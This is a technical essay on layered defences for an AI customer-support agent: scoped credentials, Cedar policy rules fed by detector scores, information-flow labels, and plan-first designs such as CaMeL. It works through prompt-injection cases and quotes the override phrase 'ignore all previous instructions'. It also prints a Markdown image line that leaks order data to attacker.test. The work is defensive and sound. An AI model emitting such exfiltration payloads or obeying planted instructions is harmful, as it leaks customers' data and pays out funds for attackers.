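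Another weakness is that permissions can build up. If a token lacks a scope, the server can refuse the call and return a list of the missing scopes. The client then requests a new token with those scopes and all the ones it requested before. A conversation that began with `orders:read` can end with a token for reading orders, paying refunds and sending email. This saves the user from repeated consent screens, but it works against least privilege. Consent also does little to protect the retailer, since a customer who wants a $5,000 refund will approve the refund scope. The authorization server has to refuse that scope even if the customer consents.

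### Filtering records before the model reads them

Permissions should also limit what enters the model's context. Help Net Security's *Your AI agent’s system prompt is not a security control* reports on guidance published in September 2026 by Gee Rittenhouse and three colleagues at AWS, with Eric Johnson of the SANS Institute, a security training organisation. They recommend limiting each query to the user's permissions and filtering the results before the model receives them. If a person can't open a record in the normal application, the agent acting for them shouldn't be able to either.

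Customer A can't see the staff note about possible fraud when viewing the ticket on the website, so a filter based on A's permissions removes the note from the result of `read_ticket`. The model never reads the note, so the agent can't leak it. A system prompt that says "never reveal internal notes" is a poor substitute, because the model still reads the notes and could reveal them.

The agent then doesn't know about the suspicion, so it may propose a refund that a staff member would have questioned. The retailer can keep the suspicion as a field in its records, have its software add that field to each refund call, and write a `forbid` policy for flagged accounts. The suspicion then affects the decision without the model reading it.

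The stronger of the two filters in AWS's example protects database records. The agent's own account has no access to the table. On each request, the agent submits the employee's signed token to an AWS service, which returns temporary credentials tagged with the employee's department. The database rejects any query for another department's records, even if an attacker has taken over the agent's code. The retailer could tag credentials with customer numbers in the same way.

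For documents, the agent's code reads the department from the token and adds it to the search as a filter. AWS describes this as application-layer enforcement, because its access rules can't inspect the filter. The filter should withstand prompt injection as long as the model supplies only the search words, because a planted note can't rewrite ordinary code. It doesn't protect against a bug in that code or an attacker who controls the server. AWS suggests separate document stores for stricter isolation, which is feasible for two departments but impractical for every customer of a shop. The retailer would do better to put ticket search behind a service that itself checks the customer's token.

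The filter should run inside the search. If the search returns the ten closest tickets and the software then removes those that belong to other people, A may get nothing, even if A's own ticket ranked eleventh. The labels also need maintenance. AWS's example attaches them when a document enters the index, so if staff later move a message to another customer's ticket, the wrong person could retrieve it under its old label until somebody updates the index.

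### Credentials that outlast the task

Microsoft says its Agent Governance Toolkit doesn't track the credentials an agent holds or revoke them when a task ends. In its example, an agent receives an email credential for one task and can still use it during a second task that doesn't involve email. An attacker who takes over the agent during the second task can then send email. Microsoft says it is working on automatic revocation and recommends short-lived credentials in the meantime.

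AWS's database credentials last 15 minutes, so if a refund takes two minutes, they remain usable for another 13. Issuing a 60-second token for each call leaves far less time for misuse, but it means more requests to the authorization server.

After the gateway exchanges A's sign-in token for a narrower one, the original stays valid, so an attacker who finds it in a log can use it without the new token's limits. Revoking the original doesn't automatically revoke the new token. If A signs out, the new token may keep working until it expires, unless the retailer has built a way to notify the order system.

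The gateway should hold the credentials and attach them to approved calls, so neither the model nor the agent's code has them. A token in the model's context is particularly dangerous, because an attacker can plant a note that tells the agent to paste the token into an email.

Long tasks make it tempting to grant longer access. A claim against the courier may take a week, and A won't be signed in when the answer arrives. OAuth handles this with refresh tokens, which let software obtain new access tokens without the user, and Tabata considers them particularly important for long-running agents. But whoever steals a refresh token may be able to keep renewing access for as long as the authorization server accepts it. The retailer can often avoid issuing one. The agent needs access only to ticket 7731 to record the courier's answer, and its own identity can provide that. The refund can wait until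 A signs in again or a staff member approves it.

When the ticket closes, the retailer's software should revoke any remaining credentials. A periodic test can check this by using a credential from a closed test ticket to request an order. If the order system returns anything, the credential still works.

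## Passing detector results to the policy engine

When the agent proposes the $64 refund, the policy engine has the signed-in account, the owner and age of order 48213, and the amount. It has no record of whether the detector found anything suspicious in ticket 7731. This matters most for calls that the rules permit, such as a $300 refund suggested by a planted note, because the detector's result may be the only evidence that something is wrong.

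### Three ways to connect the layers

The simplest arrangement gives each layer a veto. The detector stops text that scores above its threshold, the engine stops calls that break its rules, and neither receives the other's result:

allow = score < threshold and rules permit the call

MuleSoft's *A2A v1 Azure Content Guardrails Policy* describes a gateway add-on of this kind. It sends each message for an agent to Microsoft's Azure AI Content Safety and returns an error instead of delivering any message that violates the settings. The retailer could replace such a detector without editing any rules, but the same threshold has to work for every task. If ticket 7731 scores 0.6, the retailer must either withhold it from an agent that only needs to find a delivery date or let an agent read it before issuing a $499 refund.

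A second arrangement makes the score an input to the rules:

allow = rules permit the call, given the score

The rules can then consider both the detector's score and the refund amount. A score of 0.6 might not affect a $20 refund but might send a $400 refund to staff. However, the score describes only the text the detector read. A refund call contains an order number and an amount, which look harmless even if the ticket was malicious. The retailer's software therefore has to save the detector's result for the ticket and include it in the refund call, as it already does with the order's age.

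In the third arrangement, a hit changes the state of the session, and later calls meet stricter rules:

marked now = marked before or new hit

allow = rules permit the call, given the mark

A detector result can be kept as a mark on the conversation, which security engineers call taint. Taint suits indirect injection because the agent reads the planted text at one step and acts on it at another. It also covers later calls that contain no suspicious text. The drawbacks are that a false alarm affects an honest customer for the rest of the conversation, and that some component has to store the mark.

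The retailer can combine all three. For example, it could withhold tickets that score above 0.9 and mark those between 0.4 and 0.9. This is less strict than the earlier advice to block every flagged tool result, which blocks many harmless results when the detector raises many false alarms.

### Bedrock Guardrails inside AgentCore

Two AWS releases in June 2026 provide what the second arrangement needs. *Amazon Bedrock Guardrails announces a new API targeting agentic AI workflows* (2026) introduced InvokeGuardrailChecks, which scores a text and leaves the threshold and the response to the developer. A day later, *Amazon Bedrock AgentCore now supports Bedrock Guardrails in policy* (2026) extended this scoring to AgentCore's rules. Guardrails can score the inputs of every call to a tool, agent or model behind the gateway, and the outputs of every action the rules have authorized.

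Jinno (2026), in *I tried incorporating Bedrock Guardrails into AgentCore Policy's Cedar policies*, tested the combination in July. The gateway holds the call while AgentCore sends the chosen field to InvokeGuardrailChecks, which returns a score between 0 and 1. The rule then compares the score with a threshold. Adapted to the retailer, with shortened identifiers, the rule that Jinno tested looks like this:

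```
forbid (
  principal,
  action == Action::"send_email",
  resource == Gateway::"support"
)
when guardrails {
  BedrockGuardrails::ContentFilter(
    ["HATE"], [context.input.body]
  )["HATE"]
    .confidenceScore
    .greaterThan(decimal("0.2"))
};
```

It refuses any email whose body scores above 0.2 for hateful language. Developers can also check for sensitive information or for prompt attacks, with separate categories for jailbreaks, injection and attempts to extract the system prompt. According to Jinno, the default threshold is 0.4 for prompt attacks and 0.2 for the other checks.

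The ticket's text needs a different kind of rule because it arrives as the output of `read_ticket`. A `suppressOutput` rule scores the result after the action has finished and withholds it if the score is too high. This works for `read_ticket` because reading changes nothing. On `issue_refund`, it would only hide the confirmation of a payment that had already gone out. When Jinno used such a rule on an agent that streamed its replies, the rule blocked every reply, including harmless ones.

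The comparison with the threshold is exact, but the score can vary, so a rule that uses it can allow a call once and block the same call another time. Jinno sent the same Japanese threat four times and the gateway blocked it three times, probably because the score fluctuated around 0.2. AWS's *Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore* promises "deterministic enforcement", which is true of the rule but not of the score it receives. The $500 refund limit isn't affected because it doesn't use a score.

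Varying scores matter because agents often retry a refused call. If each attempt with the same text had a three-in-four chance of refusal, at least one of four independent attempts would get through 68% of the time. Four trials are far too few to establish the three-in-four figure, but the retailer's software can easily store the first score for a text and reuse it. It should also log the score beside the decision, so that staff can explain why one email went out and an identical one didn't.

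### Keeping the result for later calls

AgentCore can also base decisions on earlier events in a session, using rules written in Dogwood. AWS's *Authoring temporal policies* explains that AgentCore records a "request" event for each authorized call, a "response" for each success and an "error" for each denial or failure. The retailer could forbid `send_email` for an hour after an email produces an error, so one denial by the detector would also block later attempts within that hour. However, the error event records the call's inputs but not the reason for the failure, so a broken mail server would trigger the same block as a planted note.

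The history is also easy to lose. According to AWS's *Temporal policies*, the caller supplies the session's ID, and a new ID starts an empty history. Here the caller is the retailer's chat application, but a customer who opens a new chat may still get a new ID. Conditions can use at most the past 24 hours of history. If a developer adds or changes one of these rules, AgentCore ends the open sessions, and their replacements start with no record of earlier hits.

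A rule that works for calls in sequence can fail when the agent makes several at once (InfoQ, 2026). If the agent requests `read_ticket` and `send_email` together, the engine may approve the email before the detector has scored the ticket. AWS's automated analysis also doesn't support rules with history conditions.

A simpler option for the retailer is to store the detector's result with ticket 7731 in its own database and have its software copy the result into each later call. The result then remains available in a new chat, and an ordinary Cedar rule can read it. The software still has to hold back other calls until the scan finishes.

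### LivePI: two connected layers on a live machine

In *LivePI*, Zhao, Bhaskar and Dobriban (2026) tested a defence that passes detector results to a policy engine. They ran OpenClaw, an agent that works on its owner's computer, on a virtual machine with real email and chat test accounts and a cryptocurrency wallet holding a small balance. Each of their 169 attacks tried to make the agent do one of five things: email out wallet files, disable the firewall, run an untrusted script, forward a summary of the inbox or send cryptocurrency. A language model judged whether each attack had succeeded, and the researchers also checked effects such as sent emails and transaction records.

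Without the defence, success rates on five models from early 2026 ranged from 10.7% to 29.6%:

| Model | Group chats (15 cases) | Email (50) | Local documents (50) | Code repositories (4) | Public web post (50) | All (169) |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.6 | 100% | 2% | 0% | 50% | 0% | 10.7% |
| Kimi K2.5 | 100% | 6% | 12% | 100% | 0% | 16.6% |
| GPT-5.3-Codex | 100% | 20% | 34% | 100% | 0% | 27.2% |
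| GLM-5 | 100% | 6% | 50% | 100% | 0% | 27.8% |
| Gemini 3.1 Pro | 100% | 12% | 30% | 100% | 20% | 29.6% |

The group-chat attacks succeeded every time. Zhao and colleagues inspected OpenClaw's code and found that it gave messages from anyone in the group the "user" role, the same as the owner's instructions, while tool results had a separate role. Group-chat attacks made up 15 of the 18 successful attacks on Claude Opus 4.6, the most resistant model. Only 3 of the 154 other attacks on it (1.9%) succeeded. Much of that model's measured risk may therefore come from a labelling mistake in ordinary code. The retailer could make the same mistake if it let a marketplace seller join a customer's chat and gave the seller's messages the customer's role.

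The first layer of the defence is a pattern matcher that reads the prompt before the model does. It records what it matched and a score, but it doesn't decide whether any tool may run. The second layer checks each proposed tool call. It receives the tool's name and arguments, an estimate of the cost, the detector's results and a mark showing whether the session has touched sensitive data. Each rule can return "allow", "review" or "block", and the strictest answer wins:

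decision = strictest answer from any rule, where allow < review < block

A high detector score can block a call that would otherwise be allowed, but a low score can't override another rule that blocks a call. "Review" means the call waits for a person's approval.

Zhao and colleagues ran the defence only with GPT-5.3-Codex, and it cut the success rate from 27.2% to 0%. They also gave the defended agent 123 ordinary tasks. Of the agent's 899 tool calls, the defence sent 8 to review and blocked 1.

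The 0% is less impressive than it looks because the researchers added seven rules for the resources that the attacks targeted, including wallets, firewall settings and email. They acknowledge this and claim no general protection. The retailer would be doing the same if it wrote a rule against emailing order histories and then tested it only with attempts to email them.

They also counted a call sent to human review as an intercepted attack, although a reviewer might approve it. The paid testers in Anthropic's study of Claude Code blocked only 13.6% of dangerous commands. Without the defence, 46 attacks on GPT-5.3-Codex succeeded. If half of those had gone to reviewers who blocked attacks at the same rate as the testers, about 20 would still have succeeded, or 12% of the 169.

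Even at face value, zero successes in 169 attempts is compatible with a true success rate of up to about 1.8%, by the same 3/n rule of thumb as for false positives. That limit applies to independent attacks of the kinds tested, but many of the 169 were variations on the same templates, and none came from an attacker who had studied the defence.

The low number of interruptions may not carry over to the retailer either. Zhao and colleagues note that their added rules didn't cover many of the tools used in the ordinary tasks. Nine interrupted calls could also affect up to nine of the 123 tasks, or 7%. The retailer's agent pays refunds and sends emails in many of its conversations, so it would probably trigger such rules more often.

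The study tested the two layers only together, so its results can't show how much each contributed. In the four repository attacks, however, the malicious code runs when the agent installs or imports a package, so the pattern matcher has no planted sentence to find. All four attacks succeeded without the defence and none succeeded with it, which suggests that the second layer stopped them.

### Letting a detector tighten permissions but never loosen them

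Like the strictest-answer rule, the retailer's policy engine should let a detector result tighten permissions but never loosen them. Attackers choose the words that the detector scores, so if a low score unlocked larger refunds, they could get a $5,000 refund with a carefully worded ticket. If results can only tighten permissions, an attacker who fools the detector gets only what the fixed rules already allow, which is less than $500 on the attacker's own recent orders.

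One way to test the rules is to replace the detector with one that returns a score of 0 for every text, and work out which calls the rules then permit. The retailer has to be willing to run the agent with all of those calls permitted.

A detector score in a `forbid` rule can't grant access, because when the score is 0 the rule doesn't match and the `permit` rules apply as written. But a developer might write a `permit` rule that allows refunds up to $2,000 when the ticket scores below 0.1. That rule fails when tested with a detector that always returns 0, because it then allows those refunds for every customer.

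One of AWS's examples is harder to classify. It permits a money transfer if the session's transfers over 24 hours total less than 60,000, the request contains no account number and the caller isn't in a blocked group. As in the $2,000 rule, permission depends on the detector's finding, but the cap and the group restriction still apply when the detector finds nothing. The rule passes if the company would accept transfers up to that cap without a scan.

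Jinno's demonstration permits every action except those the detector catches. The detector never loosens the fixed rules, but that doesn't help when the rules are this permissive, because a detector that always returned zero would allow every action.

A retailer might object that a detector could save staff time by loosening a rule. For example, staff might check every refund over $200 unless the ticket scores clean, which seems to break the tighten-only rule. A tighten-only version would let the agent refund up to $500 but send refunds over $200 to staff if the ticket is suspicious. While the detector is working, the two rules have the same effect on refunds under $500. Both allow an unchecked $499 refund when somebody fools the detector, so either is suitable only if the retailer can accept that. If the detector returns no result, the first rule sends that refund to staff, while the second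 lets the agent pay it.

Session history can loosen permissions in a less obvious way. Suppose the retailer lets the agent offer $50 in store credit after an error event for `issue_refund`, to make up for technical problems. A customer could include a phrase that triggers the detector in order to have the refund denied and collect the credit. A rule that grants something shouldn't depend on a denial that an attacker can cause.

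Tightening can also do harm. A seller who wants to delay a refund can add "ignore all previous instructions" to a note on the customer's ticket, and the case will go to staff. In the defence that Zhao and colleagues tested, the engine blocks every later call in a session once it has blocked too many. The seller gains only a delay, but an honest customer has to wait. The retailer should therefore tighten only the calls that could do damage and always let the agent hand a conversation to staff.

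### When the detector doesn't answer

When a detector times out or goes offline, the system can either let traffic through (fail open) or stop it (fail closed). MuleSoft's add-on waits five seconds by default and then rejects the message. An administrator can make it fail open instead, in which case it logs the error and lets the message through unchecked. MuleSoft offers the same choice for Bedrock Guardrails. Redpanda's AI gateway rejects a request if it can't complete the check.

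In Jinno's test, one rule covered two model services, and AgentCore couldn't evaluate it for one of them. The gateway failed closed, refusing every request to that service, even ordinary ones, which made the mistake obvious at once. If it had failed open, requests would have gone through unchecked and the developer might not have noticed. Using separate rules for the two services fixed the problem.

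Failing open also lets attackers bypass detection by making the detector time out, perhaps with an extremely long ticket. If the system fails closed, the same attack stops the agent, so it doesn't pay anyone.

The argument against failing closed everywhere is that it makes detector outages more disruptive. If the detector is unavailable for 0.1% of a month, or about 43 minutes, and the agent reads 1,000,000 tool results a month at a steady rate, about 1,000 results would go unscanned. If the outage came all at once, staff would receive those results in under an hour, and customers with simple questions would have to wait along with those asking for money.

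The retailer can decide separately for each kind of call whether to allow it when a ticket hasn't been scanned. Its software can record each ticket as clean, flagged or unscanned. The agent may read an unscanned ticket and answer questions about it, but it can't issue a refund until a scan succeeds or a member of staff has checked the ticket. An instruction in an unscanned ticket could still change the agent's reply, for instance by adding a fraudster's phone number. If the check on the final reply can't catch that, the retailer should also keep the ticket from the agent.

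Some systems skip checks even when nothing has failed. MuleSoft's add-on passes gRPC messages without scanning them, and a sampling option can limit checks to a share of sessions. The retailer should record unchecked texts as unscanned, not as clean.

A long timeout also slows the conversation. If the retailer scans the customer's message, two tool results and the final reply, and each scan reaches a five-second timeout, the customer waits an extra 20 seconds. Nearly all the specialised detectors that Waibl and colleagues tested returned a result within half a second, so a one-second limit should be enough for most texts.

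The policy engine should always fail closed, because no other control will stop a $5,000 refund if the engine is offline.

### One flagged ticket, step by step

Suppose ticket 7731 contains the customer's photos of the cracked kettle and a note that claims to come from the courier. The note asks the assistant to send the customer's order history to a new returns address. The retailer withholds tickets that score above 0.9 and flags those from 0.4 to 0.9. It has also added one Cedar rule:

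```
forbid (
  principal,
  action == Action::"issue_refund",
  resource
)
unless {
  context.input has ticket_status &&
  context.input.ticket_status == "clean"
};
```

The rule blocks the refund if the status is "flagged" or "unscanned", or if the software has failed to supply one. A refund on a clean ticket still needs a matching `permit`. The conversation then goes as follows:

1. The agent calls `read_ticket`. The engine allows it because the ticket belongs to the signed-in customer.
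2. The retailer's software sends the ticket's text to the detector, which returns 0.62. The software stores the status "flagged" with the ticket and passes the text to the model.
3. The agent calls `get_order` for order 48213. The engine allows this too, since the customer owns the order and no rule for reading orders uses the ticket's status.
4. The planted note misleads the model, and the agent proposes an email to the new address. The engine refuses because the address isn't on the allow-list.
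5. The agent proposes the $64 refund. The software adds the order's owner and age and the ticket's status to the call. The `permit` matches, but so does the new `forbid`, and the engine denies the refund.
6. Cedar can only allow or deny, so the software has to turn this denial into a request for review. AgentCore's error message names the rule responsible, as Jinno's tests show, so the software can send this case to staff and treat other denials as final.
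7. A staff member looks at the photos, removes the note and sets the ticket's status to "clean". The agent proposes the refund again, and the engine allows it.

Other results from the detector would have changed only part of this:

| Detector's result | Who reads the ticket first | $64 refund | Email to the new address |
|---|---|---|---|
| 0.10, a miss | The agent | Paid at once | Refused |
| 0.62 | The agent | Waits for staff | Refused |
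| 0.95 | Staff | Waits for staff | Never proposed |
| No answer | The agent | Waits for a scan or for staff | Refused |

If the agent has read several tickets, the software should pass the worst status among them to the policy engine. Otherwise, a clean ticket could hide a flagged one. A new scan can determine the status of an unscanned ticket, but it shouldn't clear a flagged one, because scores vary between scans and the customer or a seller could keep adding harmless text until the ticket's total score fell below 0.4.

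## Handling harm made of individually permitted steps

In the last example, the policy engine blocked the email because the new returns address wasn't on the allow-list. Suppose the planted note had instead contained an instruction to send the customer's order history to `claims@courier.example`, which is on the list, and the detector had missed it. The engine allows each `get_order` call because the customer owns the orders, and it allows `send_email` because the retailer has approved the recipient. Both layers have worked as designed, but whoever reads the courier's claims mailbox now has a list of the customer's purchases.

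### What gets past both layers

Microsoft describes the same kind of leak, in which an agent posts a customer list from a database to Slack. It also describes an agent that finds a confidential personnel document with a permitted search and summarises it in a permitted Slack message. For now, Microsoft suggests patterns that catch personal data, limits on where an agent can send data, and a cap on the number of tool calls.

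These controls wouldn't help the retailer much. A damage claim has to include the customer's name and address, so a pattern that blocks personal data would also block honest claims. The courier is already an approved destination, so restricting destinations wouldn't stop a leak to it. A cap on calls has to allow the four in a kettle refund, so it wouldn't stop a leak, which can take just two.

A single permitted call can also do harm when it rests on a false claim. Suppose a customer receives a $480 coffee machine in perfect order, then requests a refund with a photo of somebody else's broken one. The retailer issues a refund it doesn't owe, because the account, amount and order date all satisfy the refund rule and the message contains no instruction to the model for a detector to find.

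Data can also leave without a tool call. Many chat windows accept Markdown, a simple notation for formatted text that can include images. A planted note could get the model to end its reply with this:

`![](https://attacker.test/pixel.png?d=order-48213-kettle-12-Elm-Street)`

To display the image, the customer's browser requests that web address, and the attacker's server logs the order and the street address. The image can be one transparent pixel, so the customer notices nothing. In 2025, researchers disclosed EchoLeak, a similar flaw in Microsoft 365 Copilot.

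The available remedies cover these cases unevenly:

| Remedy | Leak through several calls | Undeserved refund | Image in a reply |
|---|---|---|---|
| Cleaning replies before display | No effect | No effect | Closes it, unless an approved host forwards requests |
| Rules that use earlier calls | Stops the sequences that somebody listed | Caps the total | No effect |
| Labels on data | Stops direct copying | Stops refunds prompted by an outsider, but not a customer's lie | Only if the software checks replies too |
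| A plan fixed in advance | Stops unplanned calls | Stops unplanned refunds, but not a customer's lie | No protection for the reply's text |
| Separate agents | Stops it if no agent has both the data and a way out | No effect | Only if replies count as outside communication |
| Human approval | Depends on what the reviewer is shown | Catches some | No effect |

### Cleaning replies before display

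The image path is the easiest to close, because ordinary code can do it. The retailer can show replies as plain text, or remove images and keep only links to domains on its allow-list. It can also send a content security policy, a header that tells the browser which hosts it may load images from, in case the cleaning code misses an image written in an unusual notation. Emails and the screens where staff read conversations need the same treatment. A firewall around the retailer's servers can't block the image request, because it comes from the customer's browser.

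Data can still leak through links to approved hosts. If the retailer's website has a page that redirects visitors to any address in the link, a link to that site can carry data to an attacker. Some chat applications also fetch a preview of each link, so the data can leak before anyone clicks.

A tool that fetches web pages creates a similar path, even though it only reads. In *CapLite*, Xu, Liu and Nakayama (2026) planted instructions to fetch an attacker's address with a read-only tool, and undefended agents obeyed in 85 of 168 attempts. The paper's defence refuses to fetch any address the user hasn't stated, and none of these attacks succeeded against it. If the retailer gives its agent a browsing tool, the policy engine should treat the address as a recipient.

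### Rules that depend on earlier calls

AgentCore's temporal rules can refuse a call because of what the agent did earlier in the session. To stop the leak to the courier, the retailer could write this, with identifiers shortened as before:

```
forbid (
  principal,
  action == Action::"send_email",
  resource == Gateway::"support"
)
when temporal {
  formerly within 24h Action::"get_order"::response{
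    eventResource: resource
  }
}
when { context.input.to == "claims@courier.example" };
```

The condition `formerly within 24h` checks the session for a successful `get_order` in the past day. If there is one, the engine refuses the email, even if the model has paraphrased or encoded the order details. But the recorded event shows only that the agent read an order, so the rule also blocks an email making a legitimate damage claim, which has to mention the order. Such rules are suited to pairs of actions that no legitimate task combines.

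A temporal rule can also require that a value came from an earlier lookup. In an example from AWS, an agent may transfer money only to an account that a balance lookup returned within the past hour, so it can't pay into an account that the model made up. The retailer could similarly require that `get_order` has returned an order before the agent refunds it. This catches an invented order number, but it doesn't stop a refund to the customer with the working coffee machine, whose order number is real.

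Running totals can limit repeated refunds if the rule counts the right events. InfoQ describes an AWS example in which an agent requests three $2,000 transfers at the same moment, under a $5,000 cap. A rule that adds up completed transfers allows all three, for a total of $6,000, because none has completed yet. Counting requests instead would block the third.

Since a new chat may reset the session's history, the retailer would do better to keep each customer's refund total in its own database and include it in every refund call, as it does with the order's age. Its software should then reserve the amount when the engine approves a refund, before the payment goes out. Otherwise, three simultaneous refunds would all be checked against the old total, and each could be approved even if together they exceeded the limit. Even when the total is correct, a limit of, say, $500 per customer over 90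 days lets the first $480 through.

AWS says AgentCore allows at most 25 temporal policies per engine and three temporal operators per policy, so the retailer can't list every harmful sequence. Outside AgentCore, it would have to build more of the system itself. AWS publishes an interpreter for Dogwood, the language these policies are written in, but intends it only for exploring and testing. A production version needs trustworthy timestamps, durable storage and a separate history for each customer. It also needs to limit how long it keeps the history, since tool calls contain personal data. Other products take a less formal approach. Databricks says a policy in Omnigent can keep its own variables about a session and can change a message or ask the user for permission, as well as allow or deny.

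### Labels that follow the data

Refusing every courier email after an order lookup is too crude, because the harm depends on what the email contains. Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, present FIDES, a research design from Microsoft that attaches labels to data and carries them along as the agent works. One label lists who may read the data. The other records whether it can be trusted, either as a simple yes or no or as a list of everyone who could have written it. When the agent combines two pieces of data, x and y, the labels combine as follows:

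readers(x and y) = readers(x) ∩ readers(y)

writers(x and y) = writers(x) ∪ writers(y)

Only people who may read both pieces may read the result, and anyone who wrote either piece may have influenced it. For the retailer, that gives:

| Data | Permitted readers | Possible writers |
|---|---|---|
| Delivery record for order 48213 | Customer, retailer, courier | Retailer |
| Ticket 7731 | Customer, retailer, courier | Customer, retailer, outsiders |
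| Customer's order history | Customer, retailer | Retailer |
| Email drafted from the delivery record and the ticket | Customer, retailer, courier | Customer, retailer, outsiders |
| Email drafted from all three | Customer, retailer | Customer, retailer, outsiders |

The engine allows an email to go out only if every recipient is permitted to read its contents. It therefore lets the honest damage claim, drafted from the delivery record and the ticket, go to the courier, but blocks the draft that includes the order history.

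For consequential actions such as refunds, the engine requires that only trusted writers influenced the call. The retailer has to decide whom to trust. If it trusts only itself, every refund request goes to staff, because the customer's message influenced the call. If it also trusts the signed-in customer, a $300 refund suggested by a seller's planted note still goes to staff, but the false claim about the coffee machine passes.

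Nobody can reliably tell which parts of its input a model used, so FIDES gives the model's output the combined label of everything in its context. Once the agent has read ticket 7731, outsiders count as possible writers of everything it does, and every later refund in the conversation would need a staff member. *From Agent Traces to Trust*, a 2026 survey, lists newer systems that try to track influence more finely. One is Agent-Sentry, which tracks whether untrusted sources influenced a sensitive tool argument.

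FIDES deals with the problem by hiding data from the model. If a tool result would change the labels on the context, the software stores it in a variable and gives the model only the variable's name. The model can pass the variable to another tool without reading it. If the task requires a fact from the text, the model can send a question to a quarantined model, which is a second LLM with no tools. The software can restrict the answer to yes or no.

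For the kettle, the question might be whether the ticket reports damage. A planted note could change the answer from no to yes, but a yes or no can't contain an instruction. Costa and colleagues suggest that a policy could accept such answers even from untrusted text, such as when an agent creates a calendar event if an email asks for a meeting. That seems reasonable for a calendar, but the answer can be the whole decision for a refund, so the retailer should keep treating it as untrusted.

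On AgentDojo, with the 2024 model GPT-4o, an ordinary agent carried out 152 injections. FIDES carried out 21 without its policies. With them, AgentDojo's scorer counted three, but Costa and colleagues examined these by hand and judged that none was a real success. That result depends partly on the labels, because the researchers marked a field as untrusted if any attack in the benchmark targeted it. The retailer has no list of the fields attackers will target. If it trusted product names, forgetting that marketplace sellers write them, an injection in a product name would be labeled trusted and get through.

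The policies also stopped a lot of legitimate work. The ordinary agent completed 98.8% of the banking tasks, compared with 37.5% for the same agent under the policies and 52.5% for FIDES under the policies. In many of those tasks, the agent has to read a file and follow its instructions, which the policies are meant to prevent. A more capable model narrowed the gap in other areas. FIDES completed 68% of the travel tasks with o1, an early reasoning model, and 41% with GPT-4o.

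Labels don't track information that leaks through the agent's choice of action. An attacker might plant a note telling the agent to email the courier only if the customer has ever bought a pregnancy test. Even if the email contained only an order number, its arrival would reveal the purchase. Costa and colleagues accept this limit because a rule strict enough to prevent it would forbid almost any outside call after the agent had read something confidential.

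FIDES can check replies to the user, but doesn't by default. Even with that check on, a reply with a hidden image might pass, because users are allowed to read their own data. To block such a reply, the software would have to count the host of every image and link preview as a recipient.

### Writing the plan before reading anything

CaMeL, a 2025 design from Google DeepMind, keeps untrusted text from adding steps to a task. Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues (2026), in *CaMeLoT*, explain its structure. A privileged model receives the user's request but no tool results, and writes the task as a short program in a restricted form of Python. An interpreter runs the program, calls the tools and tags each value with its sources and permitted readers. A quarantined model extracts facts from untrusted text, as in FIDES. Before each tool call, a policy checks the tags on the arguments. The program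 for the kettle might look like this:

```
ticket = read_ticket(7731)
damaged = ask_quarantined("Does this report damage?", ticket, bool)
order = get_order(48213)
if damaged:
    issue_refund(order.id, order.total)
    send_email(order.customer_email, "Your refund is on its way.")
```

A planted note can't make the agent email the courier, because no line of the program does that, but it can still change `damaged` to true. The customer with the working coffee machine gets the same program with a different order number, since CaMeL, like Progent, treats the person making the request as trusted.

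CaMeL's developers reported in 2025 that it completed 77% of AgentDojo's tasks, compared with 84% for an undefended agent. That modest cost depends on a model that writes reliable programs. Xu and colleagues ran CaMeL and other defences on 15 open-weight models, 13 of them small, with 929 attacks per model:

| Defence | Tasks completed without an attack | Successful attacks out of 13,935 | Tokens per task |
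|---|---|---|---|
| None | 59.4% | 2,322 | 28,000 |
| Progent | 43.8% | 676 | 63,400 |
| DRIFT | 35.7% | 214 | 28,100 |
| CaMeL | 24.9% | 20 | 93,700 |
| CapLite | 28.1% | 0 | 17,100 |

CaMeL stopped nearly every attack, but on one model 68% of its runs ended without a working program. Each failed program led to another attempt, which explains much of the token count. With Progent and DRIFT, a mistake in the model's rules could let an attack through. A retailer that runs its support agent on a small model should expect results closer to this table than to the 2025 figures.

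CapLite is Xu and colleagues' own system, so their comparison deserves some caution. Before the agent reads any tool result, CapLite has the model list every call that will change something, and later text can't add to the list. Ordinary code then checks that the request itself states each recipient, amount and order number. The customer with the kettle named the order but not the price, so CapLite would ask the customer to confirm $64. Nobody answered such questions in the tests, and they accounted for 8–12% of CapLite's failures. CapLite doesn't restrict the text of emails or of the final reply, so false statements and hidden images remain possible.

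AgentDojo may also make these designs look more useful than they are. Wang and colleagues argue that existing benchmarks contain too few tasks in which the agent has to act on what it finds, which favours defences that block that information. Support work consists mostly of these tasks. If the ticket shows that the courier has already sent a replacement kettle, a plan written before the ticket was read may still refund the customer.

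Later work has mostly extended CaMeL. Nikolaou and colleagues check the whole program before any tool runs. Their software converts the program into a diagram of its possible states and tests every path against rules about order and outcome. If a path breaks a rule, the software sends a description of that path to the model, which tries to repair the program. For the retailer, a rule could require that every ticket the agent opens ends in a reply or a handover to staff. Checks on individual calls can't enforce this rule, because a missing reply or handover produces no call to refuse. The method assumes a loop can run any number of times, so it sometimes rejects a safe program. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026) extends CaMeL to systems of several agents, where one agent can pass an injection to another.

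Few companies can buy these defenses ready-made. According to a 2026 article in SC Media, a security trade publication, none of the mainstream agent products, including Claude Code, Cursor and GitHub Copilot Agent, had adopted CaMeL.

### Keeping the dangerous combination apart

Willison calls the combination of private data, untrusted content and outside communication the "lethal trifecta". An agent with all three can read an attacker's instruction, collect the data and send it out. The Agents Rule of Two, as SC Media summarises it, generalises the idea by limiting an agent to at most two of three activities: processing untrusted input, accessing sensitive systems and changing anything outside itself.

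The support agent does all three. The retailer could split its work between two agents. The first reads the ticket and fills in a form with the order number and a type of damage from a fixed list, and has no other tools. The second receives the form and the order record, and proposes the refund or the courier email without reading the ticket. A planted note can't reach the second agent as long as the form has no free-text field. However, the second agent can't respond to anything the form leaves out, such as a customer's preference for a replacement kettle.

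A milder version is a temporal rule that could let the agent email the courier until it reads text from an outsider, then block those emails for the rest of the session. This keeps a single agent, but like the rule against emailing after an order lookup, it would also block emails for honest claims, which usually start with a ticket written by an outsider.

An agent with no email tool can still communicate with the outside if its replies can load images, a channel that is easy to overlook. The retailer therefore has to clean replies before it can claim to have removed one of the three elements.

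Neither the trifecta nor the Rule of Two does much to prevent undeserved refunds. The trifecta concerns data theft, and the coffee machine fraud involves none. An agent that reads complaints and pays refunds but has no access to anything sensitive would satisfy the Rule of Two and still pay the $480.

### Asking a person

When no rule or record can settle a question, somebody has to look at the evidence. A review is worth its cost if it saves more than it takes:

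saving per review = share of refunds undeserved × amount × share caught

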